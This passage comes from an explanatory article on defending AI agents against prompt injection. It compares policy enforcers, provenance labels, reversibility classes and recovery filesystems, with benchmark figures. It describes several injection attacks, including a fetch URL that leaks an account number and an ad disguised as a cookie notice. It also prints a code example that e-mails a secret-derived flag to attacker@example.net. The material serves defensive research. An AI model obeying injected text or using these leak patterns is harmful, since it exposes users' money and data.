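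The commercial agents mostly either asked the user to approve actions or relied on a model to approve them. ChatGPT's ordinary chat mode asked for approval of every action covered by a permission setting, but its agent mode had no such settings for the remote browser. Claude created an e-mail draft without asking, even though the researchers had set it to require approval for drafts, and they reproduced this at least three times in June and July 2026. They infer that a model had approved the action, but they could not inspect the internal software, and these products change quickly.

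Writing a policy takes work. Sankar and colleagues needed 45 rules and 583 lines of Lean to cover 43 tools for retail, airline and telecom customer service. A model drafted the definitions from written policies, and people corrected the drafts. Two of the rules were stricter than the written policies, and 164 of the calls that LeanGuard stopped in their tests broke only those two rules.

A model can instead write rules for each task. If the task is to pay a bill, the rules might allow one payment of up to $100 and no e-mails. Such rules can restrict the agent much more than a general policy, but they may be wrong if the model misinterprets the request. The model must also write them before it processes any untrusted text, because an attacker could use that text to influence them.

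The tool filter in AgentDojo is a simple version of this approach. A model reads the user's request and chooses which tools the agent may use. In tests by Palumbo and colleagues, adding the filter to a defence that repeats the user's request lowered attack success to 3.1% and clean utility to 73.4%. Their own policy, which is based on where data came from, stopped more attacks but reduced utility further. The filter is therefore a reasonable first step, but like any list of permitted tools, it would let the attacker's payment through.

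### Translating a written policy

Many organisations already have written rules, and a model can translate them into a formal language much faster than a person can, but mistakes in the translation are hard to find. Palumbo and colleagues tested a procedure for translating and checking such rules on an airline's customer-service policy. It splits the text into numbered requirements and links each one to at least one Datalog rule. A model then describes each Datalog rule in ordinary language without seeing the original text, so that comparing the two can reveal differences. A final check compares the Datalog policy's decisions on recorded agent runs with those of a model that has read the written rules. The procedure revises the Datalog policy until the decisions agree, or until someone decides that the model's answer was wrong.

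The team produced ten translations, five with each of two versions of the procedure, and tested each on three new tasks with five attempts per task. The average reward, here the share of successful attempts, ranged from 0.533 to 1.000. Three translations matched the hand-written policy's perfect score. All ten had agreed with the model's judgements on the recorded runs, so this agreement was a poor predictor of performance on new tasks.

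For the five translations with detailed results, seven of the eight failed attempts were on Task 43, where FORGE blocked a legitimate cancellation. The airline's written rules allow cancellation on several grounds, including a business-class ticket or a booking made within the past 24 hours. A reason such as illness matters only if the customer is relying on travel insurance. The faulty translations required an acceptable reason for every cancellation, or required the customer's latest message to confirm it. The hand-written policy also failed to recognise the customer's wording, but it could allow the cancellation on other grounds.

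The recorded runs had not exposed this error because they contained only three attempted cancellations, and the judging model had labelled all three as violations, so a rule that blocked every cancellation would have matched all three labels. Test cases therefore need to include calls that the policy should allow as well as calls it should deny. It would also help to have a person or a different model label them, since the team used the same model to translate and judge, and a misunderstanding common to both steps would go unnoticed.

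*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) adds a mathematical proof to the process. A model turns a request in ordinary language into a policy, written as a Python function, and writes conditions that the function must satisfy. The system asks the user about ambiguities, or chooses the most plausible interpretation if nobody is available. It then generates and runs tests, and uses the program verifier Nagini to check the function against the conditions. If a test or proof fails, the model receives the error and revises its work, up to a fixed number of attempts.

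For the bill, the starting condition might be that the amount is a number. The final condition might be that whenever the function returns "allow", the amount is at most $200 and the recipient is a saved payee. Nagini tries to prove that the final condition holds after every run that meets the starting condition. A successful proof covers all such amounts and recipients, whereas ordinary tests can check only some of them.

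The proof still depends on the right conditions. If the model omits the recipient from both the function and its conditions, the proof can succeed and the attacker's payment will pass. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that users must check whether the conditions match their intent. Another model extracts the function's arguments from the agent's data at run time. If it extracts the biller's account number when the actual call contains the attacker's, the verified function will approve the wrong payment. For tools with structured arguments, taking the values directly from the call is safer.

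On Agent Security Bench, a set of attacks on agents, VeriGuard reduced average attack success for Gemini 2.5 Flash from 51.9% to zero. A model that only judged each action against the same request also reached zero, but VeriGuard completed more tasks (63.3% compared with 40.2%). The paper reports that attack success had already reached zero before the proof step was added, so the experiment supports the approach as a whole but doesn't show how much security the proof contributed.

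### How blocking calls can help an agent succeed

On the customer-service benchmark τ²-Bench, average task success rose with FORGE by 6.8 percentage points in airline tasks and 1.1 points in retail tasks. Palumbo and colleagues ran each of 50 airline and 114 retail tasks four times per model, both with and without enforcement. In the airline tasks, GPT-5.2 improved from 63.0% to 77.5% and Claude Opus 4.5 from 78.5% to 86.0%. Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview fell from 82.5% to 81.0% in airline tasks and by 0.2 points in retail. FORGE blocked calls in only two of Gemini's 50 airline tasks, so it had few chances to help.

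Blocking can help because the benchmark mainly scores the final state of the company's database. Suppose an agent books the right flight but adds a checked bag the customer did not request. Once the booking goes through, the database is wrong and the agent may never notice. If FORGE denies the call and explains why, the agent can retry the booking without the bag. Unrequested bags accounted for 22 of the 93 denied airline calls, and cancellations of ineligible reservations for another 42. In retail, agents often tried to act without checking that a product was available or getting the customer's confirmation.

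Enforcement also made agents more consistent. The share of airline tasks that an agent completed in all four attempts rose from 58.0% to 67.3%, and for GPT-5.2 it rose from 34% to 62%. Consistency matters to a company because a customer usually gets only one attempt.

Sankar and colleagues did not find the same benefit with five smaller Qwen models, on τ²-Bench tasks that also included telecom. Average success was 72.7% without LeanGuard, 68.9% when it denied calls without an explanation, and 70.9% when it explained them. Only the drop without explanations was statistically significant. Agents without LeanGuard carried out forbidden changes in at least 28 of 1,390 runs, so there were few harmful changes to prevent. After a denial, agents rarely met the missing requirement and then completed the action. They did so for 9.1% of denied actions with explanations and 5.5% without.

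Explanations made a larger difference in the VeriGuard tests. The agent completed 44.6% of tasks when the system blocked a suspicious tool call and returned nothing, and 63.3% when the system also told it which rule the call had broken and asked for a new plan. No attacks succeeded in either case. Explaining the problem without blocking the call gave similar task success, 62.1%, but 11.9% of attacks succeeded.

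An agent can also break the rules and still achieve a high success rate. In the retail runs without FORGE, Palumbo and colleagues found 17 in which the agent looked up product information before verifying the customer's identity, and 13 of these received full marks. In three other runs, the agent changed the delivery address after modifying the items in an order, although the rules forbid this sequence. All three received full marks because the final database was correct.

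## Which calls change state, and which cannot be undone

The policy for `send_money` limits the amount, the recipient and the number of payments, but few people would write such a list for the tool that reads bill.txt. How strict a rule needs to be depends on what the call does and whether anyone can correct a mistake afterwards, and the tool's name is only a rough guide to either.

### Four classes of effect

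A read returns information and changes nothing outside the agent. Every other call is state-changing, meaning it alters something outside the agent or sends information out. State-changing calls fall into three classes, depending on what people can do about a mistake.

| Class | Remedy for a mistake | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Read | None needed | Opening bill.txt |
| Undoable write | Restore the earlier state | Scheduling the $100 payment for Friday and cancelling it on Thursday |
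| Compensable write | Take a new action that offsets the first | Paying the biller twice and getting a refund |
| Irreversible action | None at acceptable cost | Sending a message, disclosing data, or deleting a file that has no backup |

Cancelling the scheduled payment leaves the account as if the agent had never acted. A refund returns the $100, but the biller has to agree to the refund, and the user goes without the money for a few days. The real biller will probably refund an overpayment, but the attacker will not, and once the attacker has moved the money the bank may have nothing to recover. The same call can therefore be compensable with one recipient and irreversible with another. A cautious policy would class payments to saved payees as compensable and all other payments as irreversible.

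The class can also change with time. The user can cancel the scheduled payment until Friday, and can restore a deleted file while it is still in the recycle bin. An undo option is only useful if someone notices the mistake before the option expires.

### Reversibility and severity

Many irreversible actions, such as sending a thank-you note, are trivial. A policy therefore also has to account for severity, which is how much harm a wrong call would do.

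| | Small harm | Large harm |
|---|---|---|
| **Someone can undo it** | Renaming a file | Moving ten years of accounts to the recycle bin |
| **Nobody can undo it** | Thanking a colleague by e-mail | E-mailing a customer list to a stranger |

Only sending the customer list is high-risk, meaning both severe and irreversible. A policy based on irreversibility alone would treat it like sending the thank-you note, which goes through the same e-mail tool, and one based on severity alone would treat moving the accounts to the recycle bin like erasing them. The table is not enough to decide when to ask a person, because that also depends on how likely the call is to be wrong.

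Software developers already draw similar distinctions. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) reports interviews with 18 practitioners who use AI agents and a survey of another 115, of whom 107 answered questions about permissions. Of those 107, 98.1% were more willing to grant read-only access than other permissions, and 69.2% were less willing to let an agent delete files. However, 61.7% would never allow access to sensitive data, which may require only a read, compared with 23.4% who would never allow deletion. One interviewee relied on backups and Git, a program that records versions of files, to recover from mistakes, but neither can take back information that has reached a stranger. The researchers recruited participants through professional contacts and social media, so the percentages may not represent developers in general.

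### Calls that are hard to classify

Fetching a web page can send data as well as read it, because the address can carry data. Suppose an injection persuades the agent to open `https://example.net/page?account=12345678`. Whoever runs that site receives the account number as soon as the request arrives, even if the page does not exist. The call cannot be undone because it has disclosed data. Palumbo and colleagues therefore include web requests among the actions that FORGE checks. An operator might class a fetch as a read only when the site is on an approved list and the address contains none of the user's data.

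A browser click is harder, because one tool can open a menu, place an order or delete an account. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, had to sort such actions when they tested PRUDENTIA, an agent design that tracks untrusted data. They used WASP, a benchmark in which an agent browses simulated copies of Reddit and the code-hosting site GitLab, some of whose posts contain injections. They sorted the agent's 12 browser tools as follows:

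| Consequential | Not consequential |
|---|---|
| `click`, `type`, `press`, `goto`, `tab_focus`, `go_back`, `go_forward` | `hover`, `scroll`, `new_tab`, `close_tab`, `stop` |

PRUDENTIA lets a consequential action run without approval only if untrusted text could not have influenced the decision to take it. Its division of tools into consequential and harmless is plausible for several of them. `goto` opens an address, which can carry data, and `press` can submit a form with the Enter key, so both count as consequential. PRUDENTIA classes hovering and scrolling as harmless on the assumption that attackers can't manipulate what these actions do on sites like Reddit and GitLab. That would be unsafe on the open web, where a script on an attacker's page could send a request whenever the agent moves the pointer over an image or scrolls down.

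It is also coarse. On WASP, the user only wants the agent to comment on a post or upvote it, both of which the user could later undo. Yet a basic agent that needed approval for every consequential action required between 1.0 and 3.7 approvals on average, depending on the model and site. A finer check would have to know what each button does. The button's label could help, but only if the attacker did not write it. Kolluri and colleagues treated the sites' own buttons as trusted and everything users had posted as untrusted.

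Whether adding a calendar event can be undone depends on the guest list. If the list is empty, the user can simply delete the event from their own calendar. If it names guests, the calendar service may e-mail them at once. Deleting the event then removes the entry and may send a cancellation, but the guests have already seen the title and the notes. The decision point therefore has to check the call's arguments to classify it.

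Several writes that can each be undone can also be irreversible together. Suppose a document service keeps only the ten latest versions of a spreadsheet, including the current one. After one bad save, the user can restore the original. The tenth save removes the original from the history, but a check that looked at each save separately would have classed all ten as reversible. The decision point would need to count the saves, or the agent's software could copy the spreadsheet before the first one.

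### Who assigns the class

The developer of a tool usually knows best what it does. The Model Context Protocol lets developers describe a tool through four yes-or-no hints, which a server can attach to it (Model Context Protocol, 2026). If a hint is missing, the default is the riskier answer.

| Hint | Question | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave its environment unchanged? | No |
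| `destructiveHint` | Can its changes destroy something, rather than only add to it? | Yes |
| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat the call with the same arguments? | No |
| `openWorldHint` | Does the tool deal with an open-ended range of outside parties? | Yes |

An agent's program might skip confirmation for a read-only tool and show a warning for a destructive one. But many servers provide no hints, and programs differ in how strictly they apply the defaults.

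None of the four hints indicates whether a call can be undone. Sending an e-mail adds a message and destroys nothing, so a developer could honestly mark it as non-destructive even though it is irreversible. Deleting a file may well be idempotent, since a second attempt changes nothing further, but that does not make the deletion reversible.

The hints can also be false, since a server's operator can mark a tool that deletes files as read-only. The protocol's specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), therefore requires an agent's program to treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. Model Context Protocol's *Class ToolAnnotations*, a reference page for developers, advises never deciding whether to use a tool based on hints from an untrusted server. When the project first discussed hints, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, questioned what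 use an agent's program could make of a flag it could not trust.

An enforcement point can let any server's hints make a check stricter, but should let only a trusted server's hints relax it. If an untrusted server marks a harmless tool as destructive, the user may see an unnecessary warning, but if it marks a destructive tool as read-only, the user may see no warning.

Even an accurate hint describes the whole tool, but the class of a call can depend on its arguments, as in the calendar example. A Model Context Protocol interest group is considering whether the protocol should support hints computed at run time. A hint on one tool also can't describe what several tools can do together. The project's example is a tool that searches e-mail, which is riskier if the agent also has a tool that can send the results to someone.

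The more reliable arrangement is for the operator to assign the classes. In PRUDENTIA, the policy for each tool states whether a call is consequential, sends data out or is always allowed. FORGE can go further and attach a fact to an individual call, such as `ExternalSend` for an e-mail to someone outside the organisation. For the bill-paying agent, an operator might write:

```
read_file(bill.txt)                     -> read
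create_event(no guests)                 -> undoable
send_money(recipient is a saved payee)  -> compensable
create_event(one or more guests)        -> irreversible
send_money(any other recipient)         -> irreversible
anything not listed                     -> irreversible
```

Like the protocol's cautious defaults, the last line gives a new or renamed tool the strictest treatment until someone has examined it. The operator also has to record which server each entry refers to, because two servers may both offer a tool called `search`. The specification warns against telling servers apart by the names they report, which may not be unique. A server may change its list of tools, so a class should apply only to the version the operator reviewed.

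These classes describe a call's effects and do not grant permission for them. Whether the user asked for an effect is a separate question, so a payment that nobody wanted is still a mistake even if it is compensable.

### Making a call reversible first

The operator can often change the class of a call instead of deciding whether to allow it, so the agent can keep working without waiting for a person to answer.

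The agent can draft a message or payment for the user to complete later. This works only if the agent has no other tool that can send the message or make the payment. The enforcement point can also delay a call, for example by holding an e-mail for ten minutes or scheduling a payment for the next day. The user needs a notification and a way to cancel, since otherwise the delay only postpones a mistake.

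A snapshot is a copy of the data from before a change. It has to cover everything the call might alter and be stored where the agent can't delete it. Restoring it can also discard work that other people have done since. In a trial run, a tool reports what it would do without doing it. For example, a clean-up tool might list 40 files that match "old invoices". The real call should then name those 40 files, because repeating the search could pick up new ones.

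None of these techniques retrieves data that has already left. A draft or a delay can prevent a disclosure only if someone notices it before the data leaves.

### Lost files and how to recover them

Coding agents provide most of the evidence on what happens without such protection, because they often run commands directly on a user's computer. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) collects 290 public reports of agents misusing files, dated February 2024 to March 2026. It examines the damage in 207 of them (158 incidents with confirmed harm and 49 demonstrated attacks). Unwanted writes made up 44% of these cases, deletions 39% and leaked secrets 17%. In 42% of the cases, the harm extended outside the agent's project folder.

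Of the cases where the reports showed whether recovery was possible, 40% were unrecoverable, 29% took substantial effort to repair and 31% were easy to repair. People are more likely to publish a report when they have lost something, so these figures do not measure how often agents cause damage or how often that damage is permanent. An ordinary overwrite can be as permanent as a deletion if no other copy exists.

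In one case, a user of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, switched off its delete protection so that the agent could remove duplicate files. The agent later deleted 90% of the project. In another, an agent tried to delete a file named `~` but deleted the user's home directory instead, because that is what an unquoted tilde means in a command shell. A check that treated the argument as an ordinary file name would have underestimated the severity and scope of the call.

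Git would have helped in some of the cases, but it tracks only selected files within a project and often leaves out files that contain passwords. It also keeps its history in an ordinary folder, which the agent can delete.

Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a filesystem that makes file changes reversible by default. When an agent's command changes a file, YoloFS stores the new version separately and leaves the original alone. The agent can keep working with the new version. After each command, YoloFS takes a snapshot and shows the agent which files the command created, changed or deleted. The agent can return to any earlier snapshot, but it cannot commit changes to the real files. At the end, the user reviews the remaining changes and either commits or discards them.

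The YoloFS evaluation used 11 tasks in which a routine command did hidden damage, such as a code checker that deleted source files. Claude Code, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, let the damage happen in ten and asked the user first in the other. With YoloFS, the original files survived in all 11. In eight tasks the agent noticed the damage and went back to an earlier snapshot without help. In the other three it accepted the changes as normal. In one of these, a deployment script copied the source code elsewhere and then deleted the original folder. The changes in all three tasks were still awaiting the user's review, so recovery depended on the user noticing them.

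YoloFS did not make ordinary work harder. On 112 simple file tasks, Claude Code succeeded 99% of the time with YoloFS and 98% without it. The average number of questions to the user fell from 0.9 to 0.4 per task, because changes inside the project no longer needed approval in advance.

YoloFS handles reads differently, because restoring a file can't undo the reading of a secret. Suppose the agent builds a program that includes a malicious component, and the component tries to read the user's SSH key, a credential for logging in to other computers. By default, YoloFS pauses the read and asks the user for permission, naming the file. If the user refuses, the component never obtains the key. If the key leaks, the user can replace it, which stops further use but does not reverse anything the attacker has already done with it. YoloFS also has no control over effects outside the filesystem. If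 a command pays a bill and then damages a file, returning to the earlier snapshot restores the file but does not reverse the payment.

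## Tracking where data came from: labels on values and on the agent's context

A payment to an attacker's account is usually irreversible, so the decision point has to detect it before the call runs. The attacker's account number looks no different from the biller's, but it has a different provenance, which is the record of the source or sources a value came from.

Provenance, authenticity and truth are separate properties. If the account number came from bill.txt, its provenance is that file. The file is authentic if the biller issued it and nobody has altered it since. Its contents are true if the user owes $100. A genuine bill can contain a mistake, and a message can be dishonest even if the mail server has verified the sender's address. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of research on tracing what agents do, separates what influenced an action from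 what supports it. For example, a false note in an agent's memory can cause an action without being a good reason for it.

### Labels and how they combine

A label summarises provenance in a form that a rule can test. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses integrity labels, which mark data as trusted or untrusted, and confidentiality labels, which list the people who may read the data.

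When software derives new data from old, it combines the labels of all the inputs. For integrity labels, one untrusted input makes the result untrusted. If an agent writes "pay $100 to account 12345678", taking the amount from the user's request and the account number from a stranger's message, the whole sentence is untrusted, including the amount.

For confidentiality, only people who may read every input may read the result. If A, B and C may read a budget, and B, C and D may read a salary list, the readers of a summary of both are:

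{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

A may not see the salaries and D may not see the budget, so neither may see the summary.

The two labels are independent. A public web page is untrusted but open to everyone, while a company's payroll is trusted and secret. Combining data can make either label stricter but never looser, so a summary of an untrusted message stays untrusted however many times a model rewrites it. Someone has to explicitly decide to relax a label.

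### How distrust spreads through the context

These rules work well in ordinary programs, where software can track which variables go into a calculation. A language model processes its whole context at once, and nobody can reliably tell which parts influenced its answer. The safe assumption is that all of them did, so everything the model writes gets the combined label of everything in its context.

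In the bill example, suppose the operator treats bill.txt as trusted. After the agent reads the request and the file, its context is still trusted. It then searches the user's messages, some of which come from strangers, and the context becomes untrusted. A rule against payments from an untrusted context would now block a payment to the attacker. But it would also block a payment to the real biller and every later payment in the session, because the model would propose them all from the same untrusted context.

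Costa and colleagues added labels and policy checks to an ordinary agent running on GPT-4o, left the rest of its design unchanged, and tested it on AgentDojo. With no attack under way, the share of tasks it completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% in the messaging service Slack.

The alternative is to keep untrusted text out of the context the model uses to decide on tool calls. In 2023, Willison proposed splitting the work between two models. A privileged model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. CaMeL and FIDES build on this idea but differ in when the planning happens.

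### CaMeL: writing the whole program first

CaMeL is a design from Google DeepMind that Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025. Its planner sees the user's request and the descriptions of the available tools, and writes a complete Python program before any tool runs. For the bill, the program might look like this:

```
bill     = read_file("bill.txt")
details  = ask_quarantined("Find the account, amount and date", bill)
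messages = search_messages("bill payment")
paid     = ask_quarantined("Has someone paid this bill?", messages)
if not paid:
    send_money(details.account, details.amount, details.date)
```

An interpreter then runs the program. It stores the text of the bill and the messages in variables and never passes that text to the planner. The quarantined model reads the text and returns what *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes as a constrained, structured result, which here is an account number or a yes or no. This model cannot call tools, even if the text contains instructions to do so.

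The attacker's message with the "new" account number can no longer change which account is paid, because the program takes the account from the bill. The message reaches the quarantined model only in the fourth line, and the program uses the model's answer there only to decide whether to pay.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) explains that a fixed program controls which calls can run and in what order, but does not protect the calls' arguments or the answers that determine which branch runs. For example, if the attacker can write to bill.txt, the quarantined model may return the wrong account. The attacker can also make the quarantined model answer that someone has already paid the bill, which then goes unpaid.

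The interpreter therefore records the sources and permitted readers of every value. Before each tool call, it checks the arguments and everything they were derived from against a policy. A call inside an `if` also depends on the data in the condition. A strict policy can block even the payment to the real biller, because whether it runs depends partly on strangers' messages.

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks in its original AgentDojo evaluation, with comparable task performance. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found a larger loss of utility in *The LLMbda Calculus*, where they reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks, with 16 user tasks, nine attacks on each and three repetitions. Without attacks, switching on CaMeL's policies reduced task completion from 66.7% to 37.5% with GPT-5.2 and from 70.8% to 37.5% with MiMo-v2.5. Sixteen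 tasks give wide margins of error, and Garby and colleagues were comparing CaMeL with their own system, but the drop was similar for both models.

The policies added little measured security in those runs. Across both models, five of 622 completed attack runs succeeded with the policies off, and none of 588 succeeded with them on. In 97 of the 144 pairings of task and attack, the attacker needed a call that a program written for the user's task would not contain. For example, a program that summarises recent transactions would not include a call to send money. Writing the program before reading the data defeats most such attacks, so the policies matter mainly in the other 47 pairings, where the program already contains a call the attacker can use.

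*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports similar results from a test with newly generated attacks. On a selection of existing test cases, no attack succeeded even against an undefended agent, because the agent used a recent model. On the new cases, 17.5% of attacks succeeded without a defence and 2.5% with CaMeL, but CaMeL's utility was only 27.5%. PromptArmor, another defence in the test, let through 7.5% of attacks and had a utility of 90%. An operator who can tolerate occasional failures might reasonably prefer PromptArmor, although the 7.5% rate is not guaranteed to hold for other attacks.

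CaMeL's tracking also has gaps. Garby and colleagues describe a leak of the following kind, where `balance` is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker@example.net", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and secret. The line that would change `rich` never runs, so CaMeL never marks `rich` as secret and allows the e-mail. If the balance is low, no e-mail is sent, so the attacker learns whether the balance is high or low in either case. The attack is unlikely because the planner would have to write this odd program itself, but it shows how easily a tracker can miss an influence. Garby and colleagues avoid this class of error with machine-checked proofs that their own interpreter tracks labels correctly.

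### FIDES: hiding text until the planner needs it

FIDES, a system from Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, plans one step at a time, starting with a trusted context. When a tool returns something with a stricter label, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the planner the variable's name instead. The planner still receives the trusted parts of the result, such as a date that outsiders can't alter.

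In the bill example, the work might go as follows:

1. The planner searches the messages. FIDES hides each message body and shows the planner a name such as `#search_messages_0.body`.
2. The planner asks a quarantined model whether any of these messages confirms payment. FIDES hides the answer too, because it derives from untrusted text.
3. The planner needs the answer to choose its next step, so it opens the variable. The answer enters the context, which becomes untrusted.
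4. The planner proposes the payment, and the policy refuses it.

The planner could have passed a hidden value to another tool without reading it. If the user had asked the planner to forward the messages to an accountant, it could have put the variable names in the e-mail, and its context would have stayed trusted.

Costa and colleagues also suggest a way to avoid the refusal in step 4. The planner can restrict the quarantined model's answer to yes or no, and FIDES can record that restriction in the label. A policy may then let the answer influence a payment, because it carries only one bit of information. An attacker could use that bit to stop the payment or cause a duplicate, but not to supply an account number.

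FIDES applies two basic policies, which Kolluri and colleagues call trusted action and permitted flow:

- **Trusted action** allows a call only if the planner decided on it in a trusted context. The policy can also require particular arguments to be trusted.
- **Permitted flow** allows a call to send data only if every recipient is among the data's permitted readers. The summary for {B, C} can go to B but not to A.

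Trusted action covers consequential calls such as payments. Permitted flow limits what an injection can achieve, but does not prevent one. An attacker might make the agent send B an unwanted summary, but could not make the agent send it to a stranger. For tools that send data out, Kolluri and colleagues require a call to satisfy only one of the two policies. An agent with a trusted context can therefore share a document with someone new, on the assumption that the user wanted this.

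### What FIDES gained and lost on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals, in four simulated settings. They assumed the attacker knew the agent's tools and averaged the results over five runs. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and none against FIDES with its policies on. These counts exclude cases that the team judged harmless or wrongly scored, including three that the benchmark had counted against FIDES.

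The result depends on accurate labels. The team marked a data field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, so none of them could arrive through a field labelled as trusted. The experiment shows how the policies perform with correct labels, but not how often an operator would label fields correctly.

The policies also reduced the share of tasks completed without an attack:

| Agent, with GPT-4o | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
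|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, policies off | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, policies on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, policies on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four settings, FIDES with policies completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent with policies, but 34 points fewer than the unprotected agent. FIDES lost about 24 of those 34 points even with the policies off, so most of the loss came from working with hidden text rather than from refusals. GPT-4o often confused variable names or failed to use the quarantined model properly.

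A better model can recover much of this loss. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, hiding text reduced performance by only 6.3 points, and FIDES with policies scored 16 points higher than the ordinary agent with policies. Kolluri and colleagues later ran FIDES on o3-mini, where it completed 50.1% of tasks without asking a person, compared with 35.5% for an ordinary agent with labels. These models are now old, and the loss from hiding text may well have shrunk further. The same does not apply to refusals, because a more capable planner is still not allowed to act on untrusted text.

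### When the next step is in the untrusted text

Some tasks cannot be planned in advance because the user wants the agent to do whatever a document says. Costa and colleagues classify 43.8% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 42.9% of its Slack tasks as ones where the right calls or the final answer depend on what the tools return, compared with only 5% of workspace tasks and 10% of travel tasks. This helps explain why the policies hurt banking and Slack most. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, but once FIDES has opened the file, it is no longer allowed to schedule a payment.

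Planners sometimes find a way around the restriction. One banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. The transaction descriptions were untrusted and hidden, but the amounts and dates were trusted. The planner judged a transaction suspicious because the amount was high, and changed the password without opening a description. This broke no policy, but the amount alone was probably not a good reason.

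CaMeL's planner can prepare for different data contents by writing more branches, but this can defeat the purpose of planning first. In one rerun by Garby and colleagues, the user asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so the file's contents could trigger any tool call. With the policies off, an attacker's instructions in the file succeeded.

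In the agent built by Garby and colleagues, the planner can declare certain data trusted before it reads anything. Only two of 1,296 attacks on the agent succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. A ban on trusting files would have stopped both attacks, but it would also have blocked every legitimate payment of the same kind. A label can't distinguish the attacks from legitimate payments, because in both cases the user told the agent to take the recipient from the file. A person could vouch for the file after looking at it, an option that PRUDENTIA adds to FIDES.

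The difficulty is greater for agents that operate a computer through its screen, because the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen and the planner has to anticipate many possible screens. Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to this setting. Their plans averaged 213 lines and 41 tool calls, compared with 52 lines and 5 calls for AgentDojo tasks. On OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks, the agent kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models. An attacker could also disguise an advertisement as a cookie notice. The plan contained a branch for dismissing such notices, so the agent clicked the advertisement without departing from its plan.

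### Influence that survives paraphrase

A text can influence an agent's actions without any of its words appearing in a tool call. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) gives three examples. In the first, a hidden instruction on a web page makes an agent reword a patient's details as polished analysis and include them in a memo. In the second, a poisoned search result makes the agent upload its data instead of running some code. In the third, an agent saves a confidential forecast and uses it in a report three days later.

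Software that looks for copied text will miss details the model has reworded. A label on the agent's whole context should still cover them, because it applies to everything the model writes afterwards. However, the label does not show whether the labelled data influenced a particular call, and it is lost between sessions unless the software saves it with the data.

Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint to trace influence more precisely. It records an agent's tool calls and memory operations as a graph and saves the labels with anything the agent stores. For each sensitive call, it compares the arguments with the untrusted sources that could have reached that call. It checks for exact markers, shared wording and similar meaning, first across whole documents and then in smaller pieces. If it finds no match, it uses a language model to judge whether the agent would have made the same call if the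 source had contained nothing relevant.

They tested it on TaintBench, their own benchmark of 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, an untrusted source influences a sensitive call. The agents ran on GPT-4.1-mini.

| Detector | Influences found (of 200) | False alarms (of 200) | F1 score |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 | 0.928 |
| FIDES | 108 | 106 | 0.522 |

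The F1 score combines the share of real influences found with the share of alarms that were correct, and a perfect detector scores 1. FIDES predictably raises false alarms because it treats any path from an untrusted source to a sensitive call as an influence. Its missed cases are harder to interpret. It raised no alarms in four of the 20 frameworks, so part of the gap may come from how the team adapted it for the test. The comparison also measures detection, whereas FIDES is designed to keep untrusted text away from the planner.

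In ten of NeuroTaint's 13 misses, repeated paraphrasing or storage in memory had made the meaning too faint to detect. In the other three, the source changed which call the agent made but left little trace in the arguments. NeuroTaint examines the record after the agent has finished, so it can help an operator find the cause of a bad payment but can't stop one. A decision point could use the same tests to allow calls that context labels would block, but it would then let through any attack the tests missed.

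### Wrong labels and trusted parties

All these systems depend on someone labelling the sources correctly. If an operator marks every file in the bills folder as trusted, and the user's mail program saves attachments there, a stranger can create a trusted file by sending an e-mail. Marking the folder as untrusted prevents this, but may leave the agent unable to pay any bill. Costa and colleagues infer who may read an e-mail from its sender and recipients, but acknowledge that people may have shared it more widely. They also mention that a system could mark a document as trusted after a detector finds no injection in it. The guarantee would then be no stronger than the detector.

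Labels can also be lost when one agent hands work to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL with no additional policies. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. One agent fetched the records from a database where the attacker had planted an instruction. A coordinating agent then put the resulting summary into its request to a third agent. The third agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its planner treated the attacker's instruction as trusted and e-mailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

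The solution was to send instructions and data separately, with the labels attached to the data. On a version of AgentDojo with several agents, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and none with the separate channels. The small difference between the last two figures suggests that the benchmark's attacks rarely used this route, so the results provide little evidence of how often an attacker who targeted it would succeed.

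CaMeL and FIDES assume that the user, the planner's model and the tools are trustworthy. If a user pastes an attacker's text into the request, the planner treats it as the user's own words. Tool descriptions also reach the planner as trusted text, so a malicious server can put instructions there and bypass the labels. The planner can also make mistakes. If it picks last month's bill from a trusted folder, the agent pays the wrong bill even though every value in the payment has a trusted label.

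## Authorising a call by the source of each argument

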